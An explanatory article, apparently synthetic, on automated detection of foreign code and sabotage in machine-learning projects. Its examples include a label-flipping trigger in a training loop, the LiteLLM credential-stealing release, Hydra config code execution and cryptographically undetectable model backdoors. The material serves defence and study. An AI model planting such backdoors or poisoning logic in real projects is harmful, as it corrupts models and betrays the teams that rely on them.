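# Automated detection of foreign code and irregular logic in machine-learning codebases

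## Unexpected code in a machine-learning project: the basic terms

A machine-learning project is a body of software that turns data into a trained model. Its code comes from many people, and some of it may be there without the developers' knowledge. Security researchers and tool makers have written programs that search a codebase for code that does not belong to the project and for logic that is unusual for where it appears. These programs are usually meant to catch theft or sabotage, such as a library release that steals passwords or a changed line that corrupts the model during training. Legitimate code often looks much like malware, because machine-learning programs also routinely download files, start other processes, read access keys and send data over networks.

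Most of these tools come from general software security. Their designers had web servers, phone apps and operating systems in mind more than model training, so it matters how a training project differs from that kind of software.

### A small project and the ways into it

The ten lines below are modeled on *Optimizing Model Parameters*, a tutorial for PyTorch, a widely used open-source library for building neural networks. The tutorial trains a network to sort small pictures of clothing into ten classes. The version below moves some settings into a configuration file, as larger projects do.

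```python
1   loader = DataLoader(train_data, batch_size=64, shuffle=True)
2   model = build_model(config)
3   optimizer = torch.optim.SGD(model.parameters(), lr=config.lr)
4   for epoch in range(config.epochs):
5       for images, labels in loader:
6           optimizer.zero_grad()
7           scores = model(images)
8           loss = loss_fn(scores, labels)
9           loss.backward()
10          optimizer.step()
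```

Line 1 creates a data loader, which supplies labelled images in batches of 64. Line 2 builds the model, a large formula with adjustable numbers called weights, and line 3 creates the optimizer, which adjusts them. The loops go through the data several times. For each batch, the program clears old results, computes the model's scores, and uses the loss function to measure how far those scores are from the correct labels. `loss.backward()` computes the gradients, which measure how the loss changes with each weight, and `optimizer.step()` uses them to adjust the weights. After the loops, a project normally evaluates the model on images it kept out of training and saves the weights to a file called a checkpoint.

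Outside code can enter at each of these points, starting with the dependencies, the packages that the project imports. The ten lines need `torch` to run, and `torch` has dependencies of its own. In *The Grand Software Supply Chain of AI Systems*, Cesarano and Monperrus (2026) assembled a reference stack of 48 open-source AI projects. Those projects declare 4,664 direct dependencies. Including the dependencies of those dependencies brings the total to 11,508 packages, or roughly 392 million lines of code. Nobody reads even the part of this code that one small project uses.

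Foreign code can also enter a project through the data loader, a less obvious route. Hugging Face, a company that hosts models and datasets for download, publishes a library called `datasets`. For years, the library let a dataset's author include a Python loading script that ran on the user's machine. NelsonGc reported in *Datasets 4.0.0 RuntimeError* that version 4.0.0 had dropped support for such scripts, and that the benchmark dataset GAIA no longer loaded as a result.

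Models can also bring outside code into a project. *Loading models*, Hugging Face's guide to its Transformers library, distinguishes a model's architecture (its skeleton, which is code) from its checkpoint (the weights). The architecture code for a "custom" model comes from outside the library, and users allow it to run by setting `trust_remote_code=True`. The guide recommends specifying the exact revision because the code may change later. Checkpoints may use pickle, Python's object-storage format, whose files can also run code when loaded.

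The loss function on line 8 is often somebody else's code. Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov (2020), in *Blind Backdoors in Deep Learning Models*, point out that people other than the operator wrote much of the code in a typical pipeline, and that dozens of contributors may be updating the open-source parts. The libraries fairseq and fast.ai compute the loss in separate modules, while Transformers computes it inside the model's code, so a reviewer who reads only the file with the training loop may miss it. An attacker who changes the loss computation can train a hidden behaviour into the model, which is one form of code poisoning.

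Evaluation usually runs on outside frameworks as well. Tampering with these frameworks can change what developers believe about the model without changing the model itself. Finally, most teams have an automated build system that tests, packages and publishes their code. Cesarano and Monperrus explain that an attacker who controls this system can insert malicious code into a release that still carries valid signatures, because the legitimate system produced it.

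### Non-native code and irregular logic

*Non-native code* is code in a project that the project's developers neither wrote nor knowingly accepted. (The term is unrelated to "native code", which means compiled machine code.) A developer who lists PyTorch as a requirement has knowingly accepted PyTorch. It is much less clear whether they have accepted a small package five levels down the dependency tree that arrived in an upgrade nobody looked at, and on a strict reading they have not. Acceptance also covers only specific contents, so a developer who approved last month's release of a library has not approved code that an attacker added to this month's.

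*Irregular logic* is control flow or data flow that is unusual for the project or for the code's intended task, whatever its cause. Control flow is the order in which statements can execute, including branches and loops. Data flow is how values move from one place to another. The definition does not depend on intent, because code rarely contains a record of it.

Neither property implies the other, and neither implies harm. Suppose a contributor copies a function that adjusts the learning rate from another repository and forgets to mention it. The function is non-native, and a tool that compares writing styles might well flag it, but its purpose and logic are ordinary.

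The code that attackers added to LiteLLM early in 2026 was foreign and malicious. LiteLLM is a library that gives programs a single interface to many language-model providers. Cesarano and Monperrus recount how attackers used a compromised dependency in its build pipeline to publish a backdoored release, which sent out cloud credentials, login keys and secrets from Kubernetes, a system for managing clusters of machines. A library like this legitimately reads access keys and makes network requests, but the release was irregular in which secrets it collected and where it sent them.

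Suppose an engineer on the team adds a condition just before line 8 to change the label of any image with a small yellow square in one corner. This code is home-written and malicious. Checks on provenance, the record of where code came from and who submitted it, would not flag it, because a trusted developer wrote it and submitted it under their own name.

Code written by a project's own developers can also be odd. PyTorch adds gradients up by default, so if line 6, which clears them, is missing from the loop, every update mixes the current batch with all the earlier ones, and training probably goes badly. Usually somebody forgot the line. But some developers deliberately let gradients add up over several batches, clearing them only every fourth or eighth batch, to imitate a larger batch than their hardware can hold. A saboteur could also have deleted the line. The loop alone may not be enough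 to tell which of these happened.

### How an analyser represents code

*Static analysis* examines code without running it. *Dynamic analysis* runs the code and observes what it does. A dynamic tool records real events, but only those that occur during the run, so it can miss behaviour that depends on a trigger, a condition that must hold before hidden code executes. Static analysis can in principle cover branches that no test run reaches, but it has to guess about anything that is determined only when the Python program runs. It can also miss simple calls. In *DyPyBench* (2024), a collection of runnable Python projects, a static tool failed to capture the call `"abc".strip()`, which trims spaces from a piece of text, while a dynamic tool recorded it.

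Static tools first turn the code's text into a structure. The simplest is the syntax tree, which shows how expressions nest. For line 8, the top node is an assignment, with the name `loss` on one side and a call on the other. `loss_fn`, `scores` and `labels` are below the call. Bandit, a common security scanner for Python, searches such trees for suspicious patterns. This is fast and is enough to find every use of a dangerous function by name. However, a syntax tree does not explicitly show which statements can follow which, or where a value came from.

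A control-flow graph shows the order in which code can run. Each statement or condition is a node, and arrows connect it to whatever can run next. In the example, arrows lead from line 5 down through line 10 and back to line 5, and another arrow leads back to line 4 when the batches run out. A program dependence graph shows which statements and conditions affect others, rather than their order. Line 8 depends on line 7 for `scores` and on line 5 for `labels`, and lines 6 to 10 all depend on line 5 because they run only if there is another batch.

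The difference matters for small changes. Moving line 6 to between lines 9 and 10 makes the program wipe the gradients just before using them, so the model learns nothing. A dependence graph that tracks only variable names stays the same, because no line has gained or lost a variable. The control-flow graph changes, but nothing in it marks the new order as wrong.

A better dependence graph would need to connect lines 9 and 10, which is hard because no variable passes between them. `loss.backward()` stores gradients with the model's weights, and `optimizer.step()` reads them there, because line 3 gave the optimizer access to the same weights. Finding the link requires pointer analysis, which works out when two names can refer to one object in memory. It also requires a call graph, which maps which functions call which, and a description of what the library does, since the analyser often does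 not have the library's source. Dolby, Shinnar and colleagues (2018), in *Ariadne*, a static analyser for machine-learning code, identify these three needs and note that they affect each other, since resolving a pointer can reveal a new call, which brings in more code with more pointers.

*Data-flow analysis*, or *taint analysis*, uses such maps to check whether sensitive values reach places they should not. The analyst names sources, where these values start, and sinks, where they should not arrive, and can also name sanitizers, operations that make a value safe. An analyst looking for stolen credentials might name any read of an access key as a source and any network request as a sink. To look for a spoiled evaluation, the analyst might name the test set as the source and line 8 as the sink, since test labels that reach the training loss will inflate the final score.

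The analysis works by finding paths in a graph. *PyFlow* (Yao, Gu and Yan, 2026) describes a framework for Python in which each node pairs a point in the program with a possible fact, such as "at line 8, `labels` contains test data". Each statement passes some facts on and removes others. For example, after `x = y`, the old facts about `x` are gone and the facts about `y` also hold for `x`. The tool concludes that a fact holds at a point if a path leads to that node from the start. When many places call the same function, the tool works out the function's effect once and reuses a stored summary.

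The *code property graph* puts several of these structures together. Yamaguchi, Golde and colleagues (2014), in *Modeling and Discovering Vulnerabilities with Code Property Graphs*, define it as

G = (V, E, λ, μ), with V = V_A and E = E_A ∪ E_C ∪ E_P.

The nodes V are those of the syntax tree (A). The edges E are those of the syntax tree, the control-flow graph (C) and the program dependence graph (P). λ gives each edge its label, and μ attaches properties such as a variable's name. The three structures can be merged because every statement and condition already has a node in each. An analyst can then write one query that uses all three. For example, a query can find each network call, follow the data edges backwards, and keep the calls that trace back to a stored password and run only under some condition on the date. Yamaguchi and colleagues worked on code written in the C language. According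 to *Adaptive and AI-Augmented Security Testing* (2026), a survey of the field, the analysis platform Joern now offers such graphs for Python among other languages.

### Why machine-learning code in Python is hard to analyse

It is hard to tell from line 7, `scores = model(images)`, what code will run. Python is dynamically typed, so `model` has no declared type and may be whatever line 2 returned. *PyTorch hooks Part 2* explains that calling a PyTorch model goes through a general `__call__` method, which runs the model's `forward` method and any hooks. The `forward` method contains the computation the model's author wrote, and hooks are functions that other code has registered to run around it. Some hooks are global. PyTorch's reference page *torch.nn.modules.module.register_module_forward_hook* describes one that runs after every `forward` call in the program and can replace the output.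 The developers intend it for debugging and measuring performance, but a few lines in an imported plotting utility could use it to change the result of line 7 without changing the training script or the model file.

Other Python features of this sort include `eval` and `exec`, which run text that the program puts together as it runs, so the code does not exist until then. Programs can also redefine operators, and *A Library for Representing Python Programs as Graphs for Machine Learning* (2022) gives the example of a simple addition with effects that the library's analysis misses. Machine-learning code uses redefined operators constantly, since adding two arrays of numbers runs a library's version of `+`. *PyCG* (2021), which presents a tool for building call graphs, identifies functions that take other functions as arguments as another obstacle. Training frameworks use many such functions.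 An analyser can include every possible call target and report many false connections, or it can leave out the uncertain ones and miss some true connections.

Configuration files move part of the program out of Python. Hydra, a framework for managing settings, lets a file contain a `_target_` entry that names a class or function to run. If `build_model` on line 2 uses this feature, editing one word in a text file replaces the model, and a tool that reads only Python files misses the change. Hydra's *Instantiate target whitelist* mentions that these configuration files sometimes come bundled with downloaded models and checkpoints. In August 2026, Red Hat's *CVE-2026-68508 hydra* (2026) recorded the problem as a high-severity vulnerability that lets an untrusted configuration file run arbitrary code.

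Hydra's developers have changed their defence against this risk. Version 1.3 has a denylist, a list of forbidden targets, but the developers warn in Hydra's *Execution whitelist* against relying on it as a security boundary. Version 1.4 adds an allowlist, a list of the only targets permitted, which must come from trusted Python code. Hydra still does not restrict what an approved function does internally, so a configuration file can use an approved function to start a process if the function is able to do so.

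Many researchers write code in notebooks, which are divided into cells, and run the cells in whatever order suits them. If two cells define `loss_fn`, a call to it uses the definition from the cell that ran most recently, which may be the one higher on the page. A static tool that reads the notebook from top to bottom may therefore analyse a different program from the one the researcher ran.

Tools that read only Python cannot analyze compiled extensions. Much of the heavy computation behind `loss.backward()` happens in compiled code written in other languages. Yao and colleagues' tool fills such gaps with cautious assumptions and marks them as approximate. This lets the analysis continue but does not show what the compiled code does.

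Machine-learning code also tends to fail without obvious signs. In most software, a serious mistake eventually causes a crash or a plainly wrong answer. Dolby and colleagues observe that machine-learning code with subtle errors may run and produce plausible but meaningless results. A poor accuracy score might come from sabotage, a forgotten line or a badly chosen learning rate, so the output gives a detector little evidence of the cause.

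### How to score a detector

The *false positive rate* is the share of legitimate items that a detector flags. *Precision* is the share of flagged items that are malicious or faulty. It falls as bad items become rarer, even if the detector stays the same. *AUROC* (the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve) is the chance that a detector ranks a random bad item above a random good one. A score of 0.5 is no better than guessing, and 1 is perfect.

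An "item" may be a package, a file, a function or a single line, and figures for different units are not comparable. AUROC also summarizes performance over every possible alarm threshold, but a team has to choose one. A detector with a high AUROC can still raise too many false alarms at the threshold needed to catch most attacks.

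## What theory says about telling malicious code from legitimate code

Such scores are needed because no detector for programs in a general-purpose language like Python can catch every attack and never raise a false alarm. A 1951 proof establishes this for every kind of software, including machine-learning code.

### Rice's theorem

Henry Gordon Rice proved in his doctoral dissertation that no algorithm can decide a non-trivial semantic property for all programs. A semantic property concerns what a program does when it runs, such as whether it ever sends a stored password over the network. A property is non-trivial if some programs have it and others do not. The theorem does not cover properties of the text itself, such as whether a file contains the word `eval`, which a tool can always check.

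Rice's proof builds on Alan Turing's earlier proof that no algorithm can tell, for every program and input, whether the program will eventually stop. Rice argued that a perfect behaviour detector would solve this problem, known as the halting problem.

Suppose that `leaks(p)` always reports correctly whether program `p` sends out the password. To learn whether some program `a` stops on input `i`, write a new program:

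```python
def t():
    simulate(a, i)           # may run forever
    send(read_password())    # runs only if the line above finishes
```

`simulate` works through the steps of `a` without giving it network access. If `a` stops, `t` then leaks the password. If `a` runs forever, `t` never reaches its second line and leaks nothing. So `leaks(t)` is true exactly when `a` stops on `i`. Because `leaks` only has to read `t`, not run it, it would answer in finite time and solve the halting problem. Turing proved that impossible, so `leaks` cannot exist. Replacing the second line makes the same argument work for other behaviours.

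The theorem assumes a computer with unlimited memory. A real computer has a finite number of states, so checking them all is possible in principle, but even a laptop has far too many to check in practice. The theorem also rules out only a method that judges every program correctly. Many individual programs are easy to judge. For example, a script that prints one number and stops leaks nothing.

### Cohen's argument against a perfect virus detector

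Fred Cohen reached a similar result for viruses by a more direct route. Cohen (1987), in *Computer Viruses*, defines a virus as a program that can modify other programs so that they include a copy of it, possibly in altered form. In an earlier text, *Cure of Computer Viruses* (1984), he supposes that someone has written a perfect detector, and then describes a program that consults it. In Python it would look roughly like this:

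```python
def contradictory():
    if not is_virus(contradictory):
        infect_another_program()
```

The detector is wrong about this program whichever answer it gives. If it classifies the program as a virus, the program does nothing, so it is not a virus. If it clears the program, the program infects another one, so it is a virus.

An attacker needs a copy of the detector to write such a program, which is realistic when the scanner is open source. But the argument has limited practical consequences for defenders. A scanner that flags `contradictory` has technically raised a false alarm, but blocking the program does no harm because nobody needs it. Cohen's argument shows that a perfect detector is impossible, but not how often an ordinary scanner will misclassify ordinary code.

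Cohen applied the same argument to tools that decide whether two programs are equivalent. He imagined two versions of a virus that each run the tool on the pair. If the tool reports that they are equivalent, one prints 1 and the other prints 0, so they differ. If it reports that they differ, neither prints anything, so they behave the same. No general procedure can therefore recognise every rewritten version of a virus, which limits scanners that look for altered copies of known malware.

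Any particular virus is still detectable. Cohen's sample virus marks infected files with the first line `1234567`, so a scanner can refuse to run files that start that way. An attacker who knows about the scanner can change the line to `123456`. Cohen expected attackers and defenders to keep adapting to each other.

### What remains possible

One option is to accept mistakes and choose which kind to make. Suppose a training project contains `if config.mode == "release": upload(weights)`. An analyser that *over-approximates* covers everything the program might do, along with some things it never does. It reports the upload even if no configuration file ever sets the mode to "release". If it finds no forbidden behaviour, there is none, provided that it models the language and libraries correctly. An analyser that *under-approximates* reports only behaviour it has confirmed, for example by running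 the program. Its reports are reliable, but it misses the upload if the test run used another mode.

Practical tools often make both kinds of mistake, and Cohen was willing to accept both to catch many viruses. He suggested raising an alarm when a program does something rare in normal use, but noted that an attacker who knows the threshold can stay below it.

Developers can also restrict the language. A settings file that holds only numbers and names cannot open a network connection, so nobody needs to analyse what it might do. Hydra's `_target_` entry removes this guarantee because it lets the file specify Python code to run. Cohen gives the extreme example of a system that can only display files, which prevents viruses from spreading but also prevents anyone from developing software on it.

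The remaining option is to enforce a policy without judging the code. A training job with no network access cannot send out a password, whatever its code contains. Cohen describes several such policies. One keeps a "flow list" of every user who has affected a file and applies a rule to that list to decide who may use the file. User A might accept a program only if both B and C have worked on it, much as many teams now require a second person to approve a change. Another uses a "flow distance", which counts how many times information has passed from one user to another, and blocks the information from passing beyond some limit.

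Cohen found that imprecise policies tend to make a system less usable over time. The only policy he considered provably safe was complete isolation, which would also cut a project off from other people's work. A policy also cannot stop an attack that uses only permitted operations. The training process has to be able to read labels and change weights, so a network ban would not stop the engineer in the earlier example who relabels every image that contains a yellow square.

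### The same code can be a backup or a theft

Rice's theorem is about whether a program does a certain thing. For malicious code there is a further difficulty, which would remain even if a tool could predict behaviour perfectly. Consider two lines that might follow the training loop:

```python
for path in run_dir.glob("*.pt"):
    storage.upload(path, config.bucket)
```

A few lines of code might copy every saved checkpoint to an online storage area. This is a backup if the team owns the storage and asked for the copies, but it is theft of the model if an outsider owns the storage and slipped the lines in. The code can be identical in both cases. The cases differ in who owns the storage and who gave permission, and those facts are in contracts, account records and people's memories.

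Cohen had also noticed that viruses use system services that are legitimate in other programs, so detecting a virus by its behaviour first requires a definition of legitimate use. By his definition, a compiler that compiles a new version of itself is a virus. His 1987 paper also describes a useful virus that asks for the user's permission, compresses a program to save disk space, and attaches itself so that it can unpack the program later. It spreads like any other virus but does only what the user allowed.

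A tool therefore needs information from outside the code, such as a list of approved storage accounts or a statement of what the project is for. Given such a list, whether an upload goes to an unapproved account is a question about the program's behaviour. Rice's theorem still rules out an analyser that answers it correctly for every program, but a tool can approximate the answer.

### From a guarded operation to a logic bomb

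The most explicit attempt to define these steps comes from research on Android phone apps. Samhi, Li and colleagues (2021), in *Difuzer*, a tool for finding logic bombs, build up the idea through a series of definitions. They start with a trigger:

τ = (c, T_c, Φ_c)

Here c is a condition, such as the test in an `if` statement. T_c is the set of statements that run only if the condition is true, and Φ_c is the set that run only if it is false. Every path from the start of the function to one of these statements must pass through c. A statement after the `if` block that runs either way belongs to neither set. The *guarded code* is the union of T_c and Φ_c.

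Let S be a security-sensitive behaviour, such as reading the user's location. The trigger is a *hidden sensitive operation* if S happens only on one side of the condition, meaning that all of S is in T_c or all of S is in Φ_c.

This is very common in legitimate code. When several processes train one model together, developers often let only the first of them save and upload the checkpoint:

```python
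if os.environ["RANK"] == "0":
    storage.upload(checkpoint, config.bucket)
```

If uploading counts as sensitive, these lines fit the definition exactly, although there is nothing wrong with them.

A hidden sensitive operation is *suspicious* if the sensitive behaviour seems out of place in that app. Samhi and colleagues give the example of location data, which a navigation app has good reason to read and a calculator does not. A suspicious operation is a *logic bomb* if some malicious code M is part of the sensitive behaviour (M ⊆ S).

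A program can apply the first definitions. Given a list of sensitive operations, an analyser can search the control-flow graph for conditions that guard them, though it may have to approximate whether a condition can ever be true. Applying the term "suspicious" requires knowing what the app is for. The last definition assumes somebody has already decided which code is malicious, and the paper acknowledges that malicious behaviour has no formal definition.

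One of their real examples shows how little the trigger itself may reveal. A television app checked whether the phone's model name contained the word "Emulator", which would suggest that a security analyst was running it on a simulated phone. If it did, the app shut down. Otherwise, the app carried out its malicious activity. Machine-learning code often checks its hardware too, usually to see whether a graphics processor is available, and takes a different path if there is none.

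The definitions also depend heavily on the list of sensitive operations. For phone apps, obvious candidates include access to the camera, contacts and text messages. In the yellow-square attack, the guarded operation is an assignment that changes a label from one number to another. A list made for phones would not include this operation, and adding it would make the list match much ordinary data preparation code.

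### A backdoor that only tampers with random numbers

So far the evidence has been in the code, even if it was hard to interpret. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) considers an attacker who leaves the training procedure almost unchanged. Its result concerns trained models rather than source code, but it limits what a review of training code can establish.

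"Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models" describes a bank that pays an outside company to train a model for approving loans. The company returns an accurate model but keeps a secret key, which lets it reverse the model's decision on any application by changing the application slightly. This backdoor is *black-box undetectable* if nobody can efficiently find it by submitting inputs and observing outputs. It is *white-box undetectable* if nobody can efficiently distinguish the model from an honest one, even with access to all its weights.

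Their first construction works with any model and uses digital signatures, which are codes that only the holder of a secret key can produce but anyone can check. The attacker adds a signature checker to the model. If part of the input is a valid signature, the model gives the answer the attacker wants. Otherwise, it works normally. Testers would have to forge a signature to find an input that triggers the attacker's answer. However, the construction does not hide the checker from someone who examines the model's structure.

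The second construction is white-box undetectable. It applies to Random Fourier Features, a method that produces a small network with one hidden layer:

h(x) = sign( Σ wᵢ · cos(2π(⟨gᵢ, x⟩ + bᵢ)) )

The input x is a list of d numbers. Each gᵢ is a list of d random numbers, and ⟨gᵢ, x⟩ is the sum of the products of matching entries. Each bᵢ is a random shift. Training changes only the weights wᵢ.

An honest trainer draws each gᵢ from the normal distribution. The attacker picks a secret list s and draws each gᵢ from a slightly different distribution, in which ⟨gᵢ, s⟩ is almost exactly a whole number plus one half. To use the backdoor, the attacker adds s to the input, which adds ⟨gᵢ, s⟩ inside each cosine's brackets. After multiplication by 2π, this is some number of full turns plus a half turn, and the half turn reverses the cosine's sign. Every term in the sum changes sign, so the model's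 answer does too.

The attacker runs the normal training algorithm on the client's own data and changes only the distribution from which the random numbers are drawn. The proof that this is undetectable starts from the assumption that an efficient test for backdoored models exists. Anyone with such a test could take a batch of numbers from one of the two distributions, train a model with them using the normal algorithm, and test the model to learn which distribution they came from. That would solve a problem called Continuous Learning With Errors, which is at least as hard as finding approximately shortest vectors in arbitrary lattices (regular grids of points in many dimensions). Cryptographers believe that no efficient algorithm can find such vectors, but nobody has proved it.

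Recent results have tested related assumptions. In November 2026 the AI company Anthropic reported a quantum algorithm for some problems on *structured* lattices, which have extra algebraic regularity. The Cryptography Incident Review Group's *Initial Assessment of Anthropic's Findings on Lattice Cryptography* (2026) notes that Anthropic found no better attack on mainstream systems that use unstructured lattices, and that other findings from the same work strengthen the theory behind them. The backdoor relies on lattices in general, so the new attack does not undermine it. Anthropic and OpenAI (2026) have since disclosed weaknesses in other widely used cryptography, which they describe as unrelated to the lattice results.

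The line of training code that draws the random numbers may look normal while the generator behind it, perhaps in a compiled library or on the provider's machine, is rigged. If the generator's source is in the repository, a reviewer might notice the rigging, which the proof does not rule out. But correct training code, correct data and the finished weights are not enough to show that the model is clean. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues suggest that the client supply the random numbers, that the trainer prove they were drawn correctly, or that several servers, at least one of them honest, generate them jointly.

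The result does not directly cover the ten-line PyTorch example, because training adjusts every layer there. The 2022 paper leaves open whether this kind of backdoor would survive in that setting.

### Replies and extensions

*Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026) points out a weakness in the lattice-based backdoor. Someone without the key can efficiently find inputs that fool the model at least as well as the attacker's, so the key gives its owner no real advantage.

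Another backdoor, for a class of deep networks, lets its owner find pairs of different inputs that the model treats as nearly identical. Outsiders cannot find such pairs efficiently under standard cryptographic assumptions. The honest and backdoored models are statistically so similar that even a detector with unlimited computing power could barely tell them apart. The attacker again changes only the random numbers in the first layer. That layer must stay fixed during training, and the later layers must meet certain mathematical conditions, so this result does not cover most ordinary networks either.

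A defender may be able to remove a backdoor without finding it. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) compares this to washing one's hands, which removes germs that nobody can see. Its simplest example is a program P that adds and subtracts whole numbers, wrapping around at some limit n as a clock does at 12. P gives wrong answers on a random 15% of inputs. To compute x + y, the defender picks a random number u, uses P to compute x + u and y − u, and then uses P to add the two results, which cancels out u. Each attempt uses P three times, so it fails at most about 45% of the time. The most common answer over many attempts is almost certainly right, and the defender doesn't need to know which inputs P gets wrong.

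For models, the method replaces the input the attacker prepared for with several random-looking inputs and combines the outputs. This requires a known relationship between the correct outputs for different inputs. The paper proves that the method works when the true labels are close to a linear function, a polynomial, or one of a class of functions that includes shallow decision trees. Nobody knows of such a relationship for recognising clothes in photographs. The method also corrects only the model's predictions, so it would not stop a training script from stealing passwords.

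The 2022 paper proposed a simpler remedy, adding random noise to each input and averaging the model's answers. Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues object that an attacker can corrupt the answers for all inputs near the chosen one, making the average wrong too.

*Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation* (Christiano, Hilton and colleagues, 2024) examines when defence against a backdoor is possible if the attacker's trigger is chosen at random. According to the paper, if computing power is unlimited, defending against a backdoor is exactly as hard as learning the function from examples. With realistic limits, defence is easier than learning, but it is impossible for kinds of functions rich enough to support obfuscation, which means rewriting a function to hide how it works without changing its behaviour. General-purpose code probably belongs in that group, although the strongest known forms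 of obfuscation are far too slow for practical use.

### When attacks are rare, most alarms are false

Even a detector that is usually right can be of little use if malicious changes are rare. Let p be the base rate, the share of all changes that are malicious. Let TPR be the true positive rate, the share of malicious changes that the detector flags, and FPR the false positive rate. Out of N changes, Np are malicious, and the detector flags TPR · Np of them. The other N(1 − p) are legitimate, and it flags FPR · N(1 − p) of those. Dividing the correct alarms by all the alarms gives the precision, and N cancels out:

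precision = TPR · p / (TPR · p + FPR · (1 − p))

Suppose one change in 10,000 is malicious and the detector catches 90% of them. In a million changes, 100 are malicious and the detector catches 90. The table shows the results at three false positive rates.

| False positive rate | False alarms per million changes | Correct alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.02% | about 200 | 90 | about 31% |
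| 0.2% | about 2,000 | 90 | about 4.3% |
| 15% | about 150,000 | 90 | about 0.06% |

Even at a false positive rate of 0.2%, reviewers would look at about 23 alarms for each real attack. At 15%, they would look at nearly 1,700, and most teams would stop reading the alarms long before that. For half of the alarms to be correct, the false positive rate would have to be about 0.009%, or one false alarm per 11,000 legitimate changes.

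Even if the detector with the 0.2% false-positive rate caught all 100 malicious changes, its precision would rise only from 4.3% to 4.8%. Flagging only the changes that set off two detectors could help much more. If the second detector had the same error rates as the first and its mistakes were independent, only about four legitimate changes in a million would set off both. Together they would catch 81 of the 100 attacks, with a precision of about 95%. But two code scanners are unlikely to make independent mistakes, because both would probably flag a legitimate script that reads an access key and uploads a large file.

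## Static analysers tested on machine-learning code

Running a scanner on real machine-learning projects can show how much legitimate code sets it off. Several groups have done this, but nearly all were looking for honest mistakes, such as mismatched array sizes or test data leaking into training. Their results are relevant to sabotage because a saboteur could introduce many of the same faults, and a scanner for sabotage has to handle the same legitimate code. All the tests below used machine-learning scripts, notebooks or libraries.

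### Checking tensor shapes before training

A *tensor* is an array of numbers, and its *shape* gives its size in each dimension. A batch of 64 greyscale pictures, each 28 pixels high and 28 wide, has the shape 64 × 28 × 28. Most operations accept only certain shapes, and a mismatch normally causes an error only when the operation runs, which can be hours into training.

Dolby and colleagues built Ariadne, an early tool for finding such errors in advance, in 2018. It analyses programs that use TensorFlow, Google's machine-learning library. They extended WALA, a framework for analysing Java and JavaScript, to read Python. WALA translates a program into simple instructions and builds a graph with an edge between two variables wherever a value may pass from one to the other. The developers also described by hand what TensorFlow's main functions do.

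The method needs a description of the input data. For a well-known collection of handwritten digits, it is:

`[batch, y(28) * x(28) of channel]`

This means one row per picture, with 784 numbers in each row, which are 28 lines of 28 pixels laid end to end. Ariadne passes the description along the edges of the graph. At a call to `reshape`, which rearranges the numbers into a new shape, it compares the old shape with the new one. Changing 784 numbers into 28 × 28 × 1 is fine, but changing them into 56 × 14 is an error because the result no longer follows the picture's height and width, even though it also has 784 numbers. The labels `y` and `x` can also reveal swapped dimensions, which sizes alone would not show for a square picture.

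Dolby and colleagues tried Ariadne on six programs, five that classify digits and one that classifies brain scans. Ariadne confirmed that the programs used several TensorFlow operations correctly and raised no false alarms. But it found no faulty programs, so the test does not show how many errors it would catch, and Dolby and colleagues made no claim about that.

*A Static Analyzer for Detecting Tensor Shape Errors* (Jhoo, Park and colleagues, 2021) presented PyTea, a tool for PyTorch. PyTea follows each path through a program and collects the conditions that tensor shapes must meet for every operation to succeed. It then passes the conditions to Z3, a solver that determines whether a set of logical and arithmetic conditions can all be true together.

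One of their examples is a small network for pictures of 28 × 28 pixels:

```python
nn.Linear(784, 120)   # multiply by a 784 × 120 table of weights
nn.ReLU()             # replace negative numbers with zero
nn.Linear(80, 10)     # multiply by an 80 × 10 table of weights
```

An a × b table can be multiplied by a c × d table only if b = c, and the result is a × d. PyTea does not need to know the batch size, so it calls it B and proceeds as follows:

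1. The input has the shape B × 784.
2. The first layer requires 784 = 784, which is true. Its output is B × 120.
3. `ReLU` changes values but not the shape, which remains B × 120.
4. The last layer requires 120 = 80. This is false for every B, so PyTea reports an error at that line.

Other errors occur only for some inputs. PyTea therefore separates *hard constraints*, which describe the possible inputs and the branches taken, from *soft constraints*, which are the requirements of PyTorch's functions. If H stands for all the hard constraints on a path and S for all the soft ones, the solver looks for a solution to

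H ∧ ¬S

A counterexample is a case that can occur but breaks a requirement. For example, an image file may have between one and four colour channels (H), while the code needs exactly one (S). A colour photograph with three channels is a counterexample. If no counterexample exists, the path has no shape errors. If the solver takes too long, PyTea returns "don't know".

A network with 24 blocks that each randomly use or skip a layer has 2²⁴ possible paths, nearly 17 million. To reduce the number of paths, PyTea keeps only one side of a branch if both sides produce the same shape and neither has effects elsewhere. For the training loop, it examines one full batch and one smaller final batch. With 60,000 pictures in batches of 64, the last batch contains only 32, which would crash a model that accepts only batches of 64.

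Jhoo and colleagues tested PyTea on 11 example projects from PyTorch's official repository. It could analyse six as they were and three more after changes to the code, but failed on two that relied on unsupported libraries. They then planted the same error in each project by making one dimension too small by one just before the loss calculation. PyTea found the planted errors in the nine projects it could analyse, taking about two seconds per project. It also found the fault in all six examples the team had collected from the programming forum Stack Overflow. These samples are small, and every planted error would crash the program. The engineer's yellow-square attack changes a label's value but no shape, so PyTea would not detect it.

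According to Jhoo and colleagues, Pythia, Ariadne's successor, could not follow some common ways of selecting part of a tensor. *Compile-Time Tensor Shape Checking via Staged Shape-Dependent Types* (2026) instead makes tensor shapes part of a programming language's type system, so that the language can reject a mismatch before the program runs.

### Test data that leaks into training

Leakage is harder to notice than a shape error because the program runs normally and reports a better score than it should. Yang, Brower-Sinning and colleagues (2022), in *Data Leakage in Notebooks*, demonstrate this with 200 rows of random numbers and random labels from two classes. There is nothing to learn, so a model should be right about half the time. Their script looks roughly like this:

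```python
best = SelectKBest(k=25).fit_transform(X, y)   # uses all 200 rows
train_X, test_X, train_y, test_y = train_test_split(best, y)
model.fit(train_X, train_y)
```

The script's first line keeps the 25 columns, out of 10,000, that best match the labels. With so many columns, some match by luck. Because the script chooses the columns before setting aside the test rows, the lucky matches extend to those rows, and the model scores 76%. Swapping the first two steps would fix this, because only training rows would then influence the choice of columns.

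Yang and colleagues' tool traces how data moves through a notebook and labels the edges of the data-flow graph. A *map* edge represents an operation that treats each row separately, such as replacing missing values with zero. A *reduce* edge represents one that combines rows, such as computing an average or choosing the best columns. The tool finds the training and test data by looking for calls such as `fit` and `predict`, then traces both back to their origins. It reports *preprocessing leakage* if the training data depends on a reduce edge from data that includes the test rows.

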